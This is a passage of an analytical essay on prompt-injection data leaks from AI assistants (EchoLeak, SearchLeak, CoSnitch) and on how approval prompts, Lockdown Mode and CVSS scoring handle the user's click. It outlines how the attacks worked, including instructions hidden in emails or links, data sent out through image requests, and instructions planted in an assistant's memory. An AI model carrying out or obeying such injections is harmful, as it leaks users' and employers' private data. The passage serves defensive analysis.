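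Fewer questions should mean less fatigue, and the questions are better chosen because each one concerns an action that the rules could not clear. Kolluri and colleagues suggest that a prompt could also use the labels to show where the data came from and who may read it. An attacker who controls the agent's text can't change those labels. The researchers left the design of such a prompt for later work.

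Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a whole document. If an email lists ten jobs for the agent, the user can declare the email trustworthy once instead of approving ten actions. This is convenient but much riskier, because the agent will also treat any instructions hidden in the email as trusted. The user has to find the attack in the email's text, without the ten chances to notice something wrong that approving each action would give.

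Kolluri and colleagues chose not to let users release private data in the same wholesale way. They kept a separate approval for each action because whether it is right to share something usually depends on the recipient and the occasion. The same argument applies, to some extent, to trusting an email. An emailed list of jobs may be an acceptable reason to update a calendar but a bad reason to send a file outside the company.

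### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode switches off many of the ChatGPT features that could send data out. The user, or the user's employer, decides once, in advance, whether to turn it on. OpenAI introduced it for organisations on February 13, 2026, and began extending it to personal accounts on June 4. The company intended it for a small group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and said that most users didn't need it.

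ChatGPT can still use web pages to answer questions in this mode, but only copies that OpenAI has already stored. No live request leaves the company's network, so the attacker's server has nothing to record. The results may be out of date or missing. *Lockdown Mode*, OpenAI's help page for the feature, adds that ChatGPT may not display images in its answers and can't download files to analyse. Deep Research and the agent mode are unavailable.

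Normally a user can approve network access for code that ChatGPT has written in Canvas, its editing workspace. Lockdown Mode removes that approval prompt, so an attacker can't obtain network access for the code by persuading the user to grant it.

OpenAI has listed the features missing from the mode but has not measured how much less work people get done without them. The loss may be small for someone who uses ChatGPT to edit confidential documents, but someone who relies on Deep Research or wants an agent to make bookings can't use ChatGPT for those tasks in this mode.

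The mode doesn't stop injections, which can arrive in an uploaded file or a stored web page and distort an answer. It also doesn't affect Codex, which has its own network settings. The help page doesn't list ordinary links or copied commands among the things the mode restricts, so users still have to judge those themselves. OpenAI expects the mode to reduce the risk of data theft substantially but doesn't guarantee it will prevent every leak.

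In workspaces that an organisation manages, the administrator decides which connected apps remain available. OpenAI advises against enabling an action that changes something in an app unless the administrator is confident that no attacker could see the result. That can be hard to judge, because even adding a comment to a shared document could reveal data to an outsider who has access to it. But the administrator makes the choice once and has time to investigate, unlike an employee who must answer a prompt mid-task.

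People with personal accounts can switch the mode off for a single chat in a couple of clicks. They are most likely to do this when a missing feature interrupts their work, and the chat may already contain the documents they wanted to protect. Without this option, some would probably turn the mode off permanently.

For users outside Lockdown Mode, OpenAI puts an "Elevated Risk" label on certain network features, including the Codex internet access setting, and explains what could go wrong. OpenAI's *Elevated Risk labels* acknowledges that the industry's safeguards don't yet fully address these risks, and advises people to turn on a labelled feature only if they understand the risks and are comfortable with them. OpenAI's standard warranties don't cover the labelled features. The label doesn't block anything, and someone who turns on internet access to look up documentation has to estimate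 the chance of an attack that they probably wouldn't notice.

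## Whether the human step prevents harm or shifts the blame

OpenAI's "Elevated Risk" label may prevent some leaks by discouraging people from using the features that carry it. It also shifts more of the responsibility for any leak onto people who use those features anyway. Clicks and approval prompts can have the same two effects, which need separate tests.

A human step prevents harm if it reduces leaks. If the leak rate barely changes but the user is identified as the cause in records, scores or contracts, the step shifts the blame. A step can also do both, by stopping some leaks and shifting the blame for the rest to the user.

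Suppose an agent tries to run 1,000 malicious commands. With no check, all of them will run. If users are asked to approve each command and refuse 13.6%, as Anthropic's paid testers did, 864 will run, each with a person's approval on record. The automated check that Anthropic tried on the same commands blocked 89%, which would leave 110. Asking the user is therefore safer than no check, because it stops 136 harmful commands, but less safe than the automated check, because it lets through 754 more.

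Notion's late warning prevented nothing, because the hiring data had already gone, but a user who clicked "yes" would still have appeared to consent.

A human approval step can also affect how much power developers give an agent. Meta's Rule of Two allows the riskiest combination of abilities if a person approves the agent's actions. If developers rely on this exception and the person misses most attacks, the agent could cause more leaks than one built without that combination. An experiment that only switches the approval prompt on and off would not measure this effect.

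### What a click takes off a severity score

The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) rates the severity of a software flaw from 0 to 10. Many organisations treat it as an industry standard, according to Wunder, Kurtz and colleagues (2023), in *Shedding Light on CVSS Scoring Inconsistencies*. Version 3.1 adds a number for how easily an attacker can exploit the flaw to a number for how much damage follows. NVD's *CVSS v3.1 Equations*, from the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), gives the formulas for an attack whose effects stay within the vulnerable component's security scope:

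exploitability = 8.22 × attack vector × attack complexity × privileges required × user interaction

impact = 6.42 × [1 − (1 − confidentiality) × (1 − integrity) × (1 − availability)]

The base score is the sum, rounded up to one decimal place and capped at 10. Each named factor has a few permitted values. An attack that works over a network, needs no special conditions and requires no account gets 0.85, 0.77 and 0.85 for the first three factors. User interaction scores 0.85 if the attack needs none and 0.62 if it needs some. A serious loss of confidentiality scores 0.56, and no loss scores zero.

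For an attack that exposes confidential data and does nothing else, the arithmetic is as follows.

| | No user interaction | User interaction required |
|---|---|---|
| Exploitability | 3.887 | 2.835 |
| Impact | 3.595 | 3.595 |
| Sum | 7.482 | 6.430 |
| Base score | 7.5 (high) | 6.5 (medium) |

Requiring a click lowers the flaw's severity score by about one point, enough to move it from high to medium. The deduction is the same no matter how likely people are to click, even though the simulated phishing emails at UC San Diego Health varied widely in how many employees fell for them.

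FIRST, the organisation that maintains CVSS, says the system measures severity and should not be used to measure risk. But Wunder and colleagues cite earlier criticism that companies often use the base score as a risk rating. A company that does so will rank a one-click leak below a zero-click leak of the same data, even if nearly every user clicks.

### The disputed score for SearchLeak

SearchLeak, the attack that began with a link to Microsoft's own site, fits the right-hand column exactly. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives it a base score of 6.5, with user interaction required, and also rates it critical. The two ratings are compatible because "critical" comes from Microsoft's own severity scale. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026) lists another Copilot flaw as critical on Microsoft's scale but 5.3 under CVSS, where high attack complexity and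 the need for user interaction both lowered the score.

A low score could affect how seriously customers took SearchLeak when they decided what Copilot should be able to read. It could not have led them to delay a patch, because Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers.

News reports disagree about whether NVD scored SearchLeak higher than Microsoft did. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw* (2026) gives NVD's score as 7.5. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) gives the same score and adds that NVD judged that the attack needed no user interaction. The Next Web rejects the 7.5 figure, reporting that NVD's entry and Microsoft's record both showed 6.5.

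Copies of the entry make it much more likely that NVD's score is 7.5. CIRCL's *FKIE_CVE-2026-42824* (2026) preserves NVD's data from June 5, when the analysis was still under way and the only score was Microsoft's 6.5. The change history in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), a page on the tracking site CVEFeed, shows that an "Initial Analysis" on June 8 added a second assessment with no user interaction, which works out to 7.5. CVEFeed hides the analyst's email address, but the timing and wording fit NVD. The Next Web may have used an older copy or mistaken Microsoft's score for NVD's.

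NVD does take clicks into account. Its *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for Wordfence as of 05/29/2025* (2025) includes a case where the security company Wordfence entered "None" for user interaction and NIST, the US agency that runs NVD, changed it to "Required". The reason given covers browsing the web, clicking links and opening files.

Missing information is a more likely explanation. Microsoft's public description of SearchLeak was one sentence that didn't mention a link, and Varonis published the details a week after the analysis. Under NVD's older guidance, analysts were supposed to assume the worst when a vendor withheld details. But the analysts did have Microsoft's assessment, which included the user interaction, so missing information isn't a complete explanation either.

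Increasingly, the company that made a product will probably be the only one to decide how much the user's part should count in a flaw's severity score. In April 2026, NIST announced that it would no longer routinely add its own score when the supplier had provided one, though anyone can request one. It made an exception for SearchLeak, for reasons that are unclear. In early September, OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-24301* (2026) still had only Microsoft's score for CoSnitch, and NVD had not begun its analysis.

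### Why EchoLeak and CoSnitch scored higher

Microsoft gave EchoLeak a severity score of 9.3, nearly three points higher than SearchLeak's, partly because EchoLeak needed no click. If it had needed one and nothing else had changed, the formula would give 8.2. The rest of the gap comes from Microsoft's judgments that EchoLeak could affect systems beyond Copilot's own security scope and had a small effect on data integrity. Both are recorded in *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), CVEFeed's page on EchoLeak.

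The later analysis on the same page, which is identical to the one for SearchLeak, dropped both entries and gave a score of 7.5. The two attacks therefore have very different scores in one set of assessments and the same score in the other, although both stole an employee's data through an image request that a Microsoft server passed on.

CoSnitch needed a click but still scored 8.8 because Microsoft recorded a high impact on integrity and availability as well as confidentiality. With confidentiality alone, it would have scored 6.5, like SearchLeak. Some effect on integrity is plausible, since the same research found that a web page could plant false instructions in Copilot's memory. The effect on availability is harder to explain, since Microsoft titled the flaw "Information Disclosure". OpenCVE's history shows similar uncertainty in a separate assessment of the technical impact, which changed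 from "partial" to "total" on August 27, 2026, and back the next day.

A flaw that requires a click can still receive an even higher severity score. MITRE's *CVE-2026-24307* lists another Copilot flaw that required user interaction, and Microsoft scored it 9.3.

Scores also vary with who assigns them. Wunder and colleagues surveyed 196 CVSS users and found that they assessed user interaction inconsistently, even for very common kinds of flaw. Nine months later, 59 of them scored the same flaws again, and 68% of those gave a different severity rating. The inconsistency had more to do with the categories than with the scorers' experience. Thirty percent had never read the documentation, and a typical assessment took about five minutes. Most thought CVSS was inconsistent but still useful.

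Given that much noise, a one-point difference between two leaks is weak evidence about which is worse. But the deduction for a click is systematic, because it always lowers the score.

### Active and passive users

CVSS 4.0, the newer version, replaces "Required" with two categories. CERT/CC's *User Interaction*, from the vulnerability coordination centre at Carnegie Mellon University, defines all three options:

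- **None:** the attack works without any person other than the attacker.
- **Passive:** the user has limited contact with the attacker's material, which the definition treats as involuntary, and doesn't have to override a protection.
- **Active:** the user takes specific, conscious actions with that material, or does something that defeats a protection.

"None" produces the highest score, but strictly speaking it doesn't fit even EchoLeak, because an employee had to ask Copilot a question before anything happened. "Passive" fits that employee well. SearchLeak is harder to classify because the employee clicked the link deliberately but didn't know it contained instructions for Copilot. Someone who pastes a command into a terminal is clearly active, and FIRST's examples of active interaction include accepting a prompt or security warning.

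The new categories are an improvement because they separate employees who had no real choice from those who ignored a warning. But they don't account for what the warning showed. If the dialog doesn't mention the attachment, an employee who approves an email to the right supplier with the wrong file attached counts as just as active as one who clicks through a full-page alert.

This gives vendors an incentive to add approval prompts even if the prompts prevent little harm. Suppose a company adds one to a tool that used to send data automatically. Any injection that can still use the tool now needs a user's approval, so its score falls. The score falls by the same amount whether users refuse nine in ten malicious requests or one in ten. In the second case, the company has mostly shifted the blame to users, perhaps without intending to. A fairer rule would lower the score only if tests had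 found that users refuse malicious requests.

### How companies treat reports that depend on the user

Under Microsoft's 2025 severity guide for AI systems, an injection that stole another user's data was critical if it needed no interaction and important, one level lower, if it needed a click or more. Microsoft nevertheless rated both SearchLeak and CoSnitch critical. Either the guide has changed or Microsoft doesn't apply it strictly.

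Companies have a reasonable argument for considering the user's part in an attack. Their engineers have limited time, and an attack that needs several unlikely mistakes deserves less of it than one that needs none. Microsoft gave roughly this reason when it closed Checkmarx's report on Copilot Chat, saying the attack depended on several unusual actions.

The argument is weaker when the user's action is ordinary. Checkmarx reported the Gemini links to Google, which declined to track them as a security bug, although people normally click links in answers.

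OpenAI's safety bug bounty, launched in March 2026, covers injections that make an agent leak a user's data, but only if the attack works at least half the time. This threshold doesn't exclude attacks that involve a click, though it could exclude an attack that works on one attempt in three.

Anthropic's security documentation for Claude Code makes users responsible for reviewing proposed code and commands before approving them. Anthropic's own experiment is the best evidence that most people can't be relied on to do this. To its credit, Anthropic published that result and then made an automated check the default. Asking users to review every command is much easier to defend if software has already stopped most of the bad ones.

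Companies have often fixed flaws that required a user's click, including Reprompt, SearchLeak, CoSnitch and RovoBlast. These fixes count against the view that vendors use the click merely as an excuse. But a company can fix a flaw and still describe it as the customer's doing, as Atlassian did when it said that a RovoBlast victim must provide untrusted content.

The general terms of service are blunter. OpenAI has told users to evaluate ChatGPT's output, with human review where appropriate, before using or sharing it. In its 2025 terms for consumer Copilot, Microsoft told people to use it at their own risk. Clauses like these mainly concern wrong answers. A user could check every fact in a summary and find no errors while an image in the same summary sent out their email. How far a court would let a company rely on such a clause after a leak would vary by country and type of customer.

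### Who should answer for the click

*Moral Crumple Zones* (2019), by the anthropologist Madeleine Clare Elish, describes how a human operator with limited control can take the blame for a system's failure, which protects the technology and the company behind it. The term refers to the part of a car that absorbs the force of a crash to protect the people inside. Elish's cases include the 1979 accident at the Three Mile Island nuclear plant and the 2009 crash of Air France Flight 447. Public accounts of both focused on the operators' mistakes, although the machines had shaped what the operators could see and do.

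The comparison partly fits an employee who clicks a link in Copilot's answer. Pilots and plant operators train for years to supervise their machines, while the employee only wanted a summary and has even less control over the system than they did. But Elish studied accidents after which people were blamed. The published reports of assistant leaks describe almost no victims, and none describes an employee who lost a job over a click. For now, the blame appears mostly in how companies write their scores, logs and statements.

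In a broader study, *The Flaws of Policies Requiring Human Oversight of Government Algorithms* (2022), Ben Green compared the human oversight called for in 41 policies with research on what people can do. He found that people mostly could not perform that oversight, and that the promise of it made it easier for governments to adopt flawed algorithms and avoid responsibility for them. Green would require agencies, before adopting an algorithm, to justify using one at all and to provide evidence that any proposed human oversight works.

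Applied to approval prompts, Green's argument would reverse the usual burden of proof, because a company would have to test whether its users refuse malicious requests before it could claim credit for putting a human in the loop. Anthropic has run such a test on Claude Code, but few other vendors have published one. Green was writing about officials who decide about other people, such as judges using risk scores. The user of an assistant is usually deciding about their own data or their employer's, which gives them a stronger claim to be asked.

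The main reason to ask the user is to get consent. The purpose of a task is often to send private information to someone outside the company, such as a contract to a lawyer or a salary figure to a recruiter. A label on the file can't determine whether a particular lawyer should have the contract today. For this reason, Kolluri and colleagues kept a separate approval for each release of private data. Blocking every such message would prevent leaks, but it would take the decision away from the employee.

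Consent covers only what a person has understood. An employee who approves sending "a summary" to an auditor has not agreed to send the raw invoices inside it. Their approval is good evidence that they wanted to send the auditor something, but not that they accepted the leak. If the approval dialog didn't mention the invoices, the company that designed it is better placed than the employee to prevent the next leak.

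Better prompts can narrow this gap. In the experiment by Hossain and colleagues, people approved less than half as many malicious requests with the best prompt as with a short description. Approval prompts can therefore reduce harm, not just shift blame. But even with the best prompt, people approved nearly a quarter of the attacks.

Requiring a click can help even when the user sees no warning. When an app stops loading outside images, an attacker who could have taken data silently has to persuade somebody to follow a link. Some people won't, and one of them may report it. However, this benefit comes from blocking the images, which removes the automatic route. If the app could also check the link, relying on the user instead would only lead to more leaks.

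*Users Are Not the Enemy* (1999), by Anne Adams and Angela Sasse, reports a survey and interviews about passwords. People wrote passwords down or chose weak ones when they had to remember many and change them often. Security departments saw this as carelessness, but Adams and Sasse found that the rules clashed with the way people worked, and that users often didn't know the threats because nobody had told them.

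Adams and Sasse's findings are a reason not to blame users, but they do not justify ignoring users. Adams and Sasse thought that people would behave more securely if they understood the threats and the rules suited their work. Having to answer 100 prompts a day creates much the same problem as having to remember a dozen passwords, but one clear question about sending payroll data to a stranger does not. Better information would not have helped the employee in EchoLeak, however, because the employee was never asked to approve anything.

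### Article 14 of the EU AI Act

Article 14 of the EU's AI Act requires the makers of high-risk AI systems to design them so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use. The people overseeing a system must be able to understand its limits, interpret its output, decide not to use the system and stop it. They must also be able to stay aware of automation bias, the possible tendency to rely automatically, or too much, on a system's output.

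The article places the design duty on the maker, so a maker can't comply just by adding a button and telling users to be careful. A separate article requires organisations that use high-risk systems to assign oversight to people with the necessary competence, training and authority. Another requires the systems to resist outsiders' attempts to exploit their weaknesses. The Act therefore requires human oversight in addition to security measures.

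However, awareness is a modest goal. Confidence in spotting problems with AI didn't help the participants in the study by Li and colleagues. A maker could explain automation bias clearly in its instructions and still sell a system whose overseers approve almost everything. Article 14 requires effective oversight, so a regulator could reasonably ask for evidence that overseers catch errors, but the article sets no minimum detection rate.

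Most of the assistants in these attacks probably fall outside Article 14. The Act's high-risk category covers AI in certain regulated products and in listed uses such as screening job applicants, assessing creditworthiness and some kinds of policing, but summarising email isn't a listed use. A tool that ranks job applicants would normally be high-risk, while an assistant that only copies their details into a hiring tracker probably would not, although both could leak the same salary expectations.

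These duties were due to start on August 2, 2026 for the listed uses and a year later for AI in regulated products. In May 2026, negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states agreed to postpone them to December 2, 2027 for the listed uses and August 2, 2028 for AI in regulated products.
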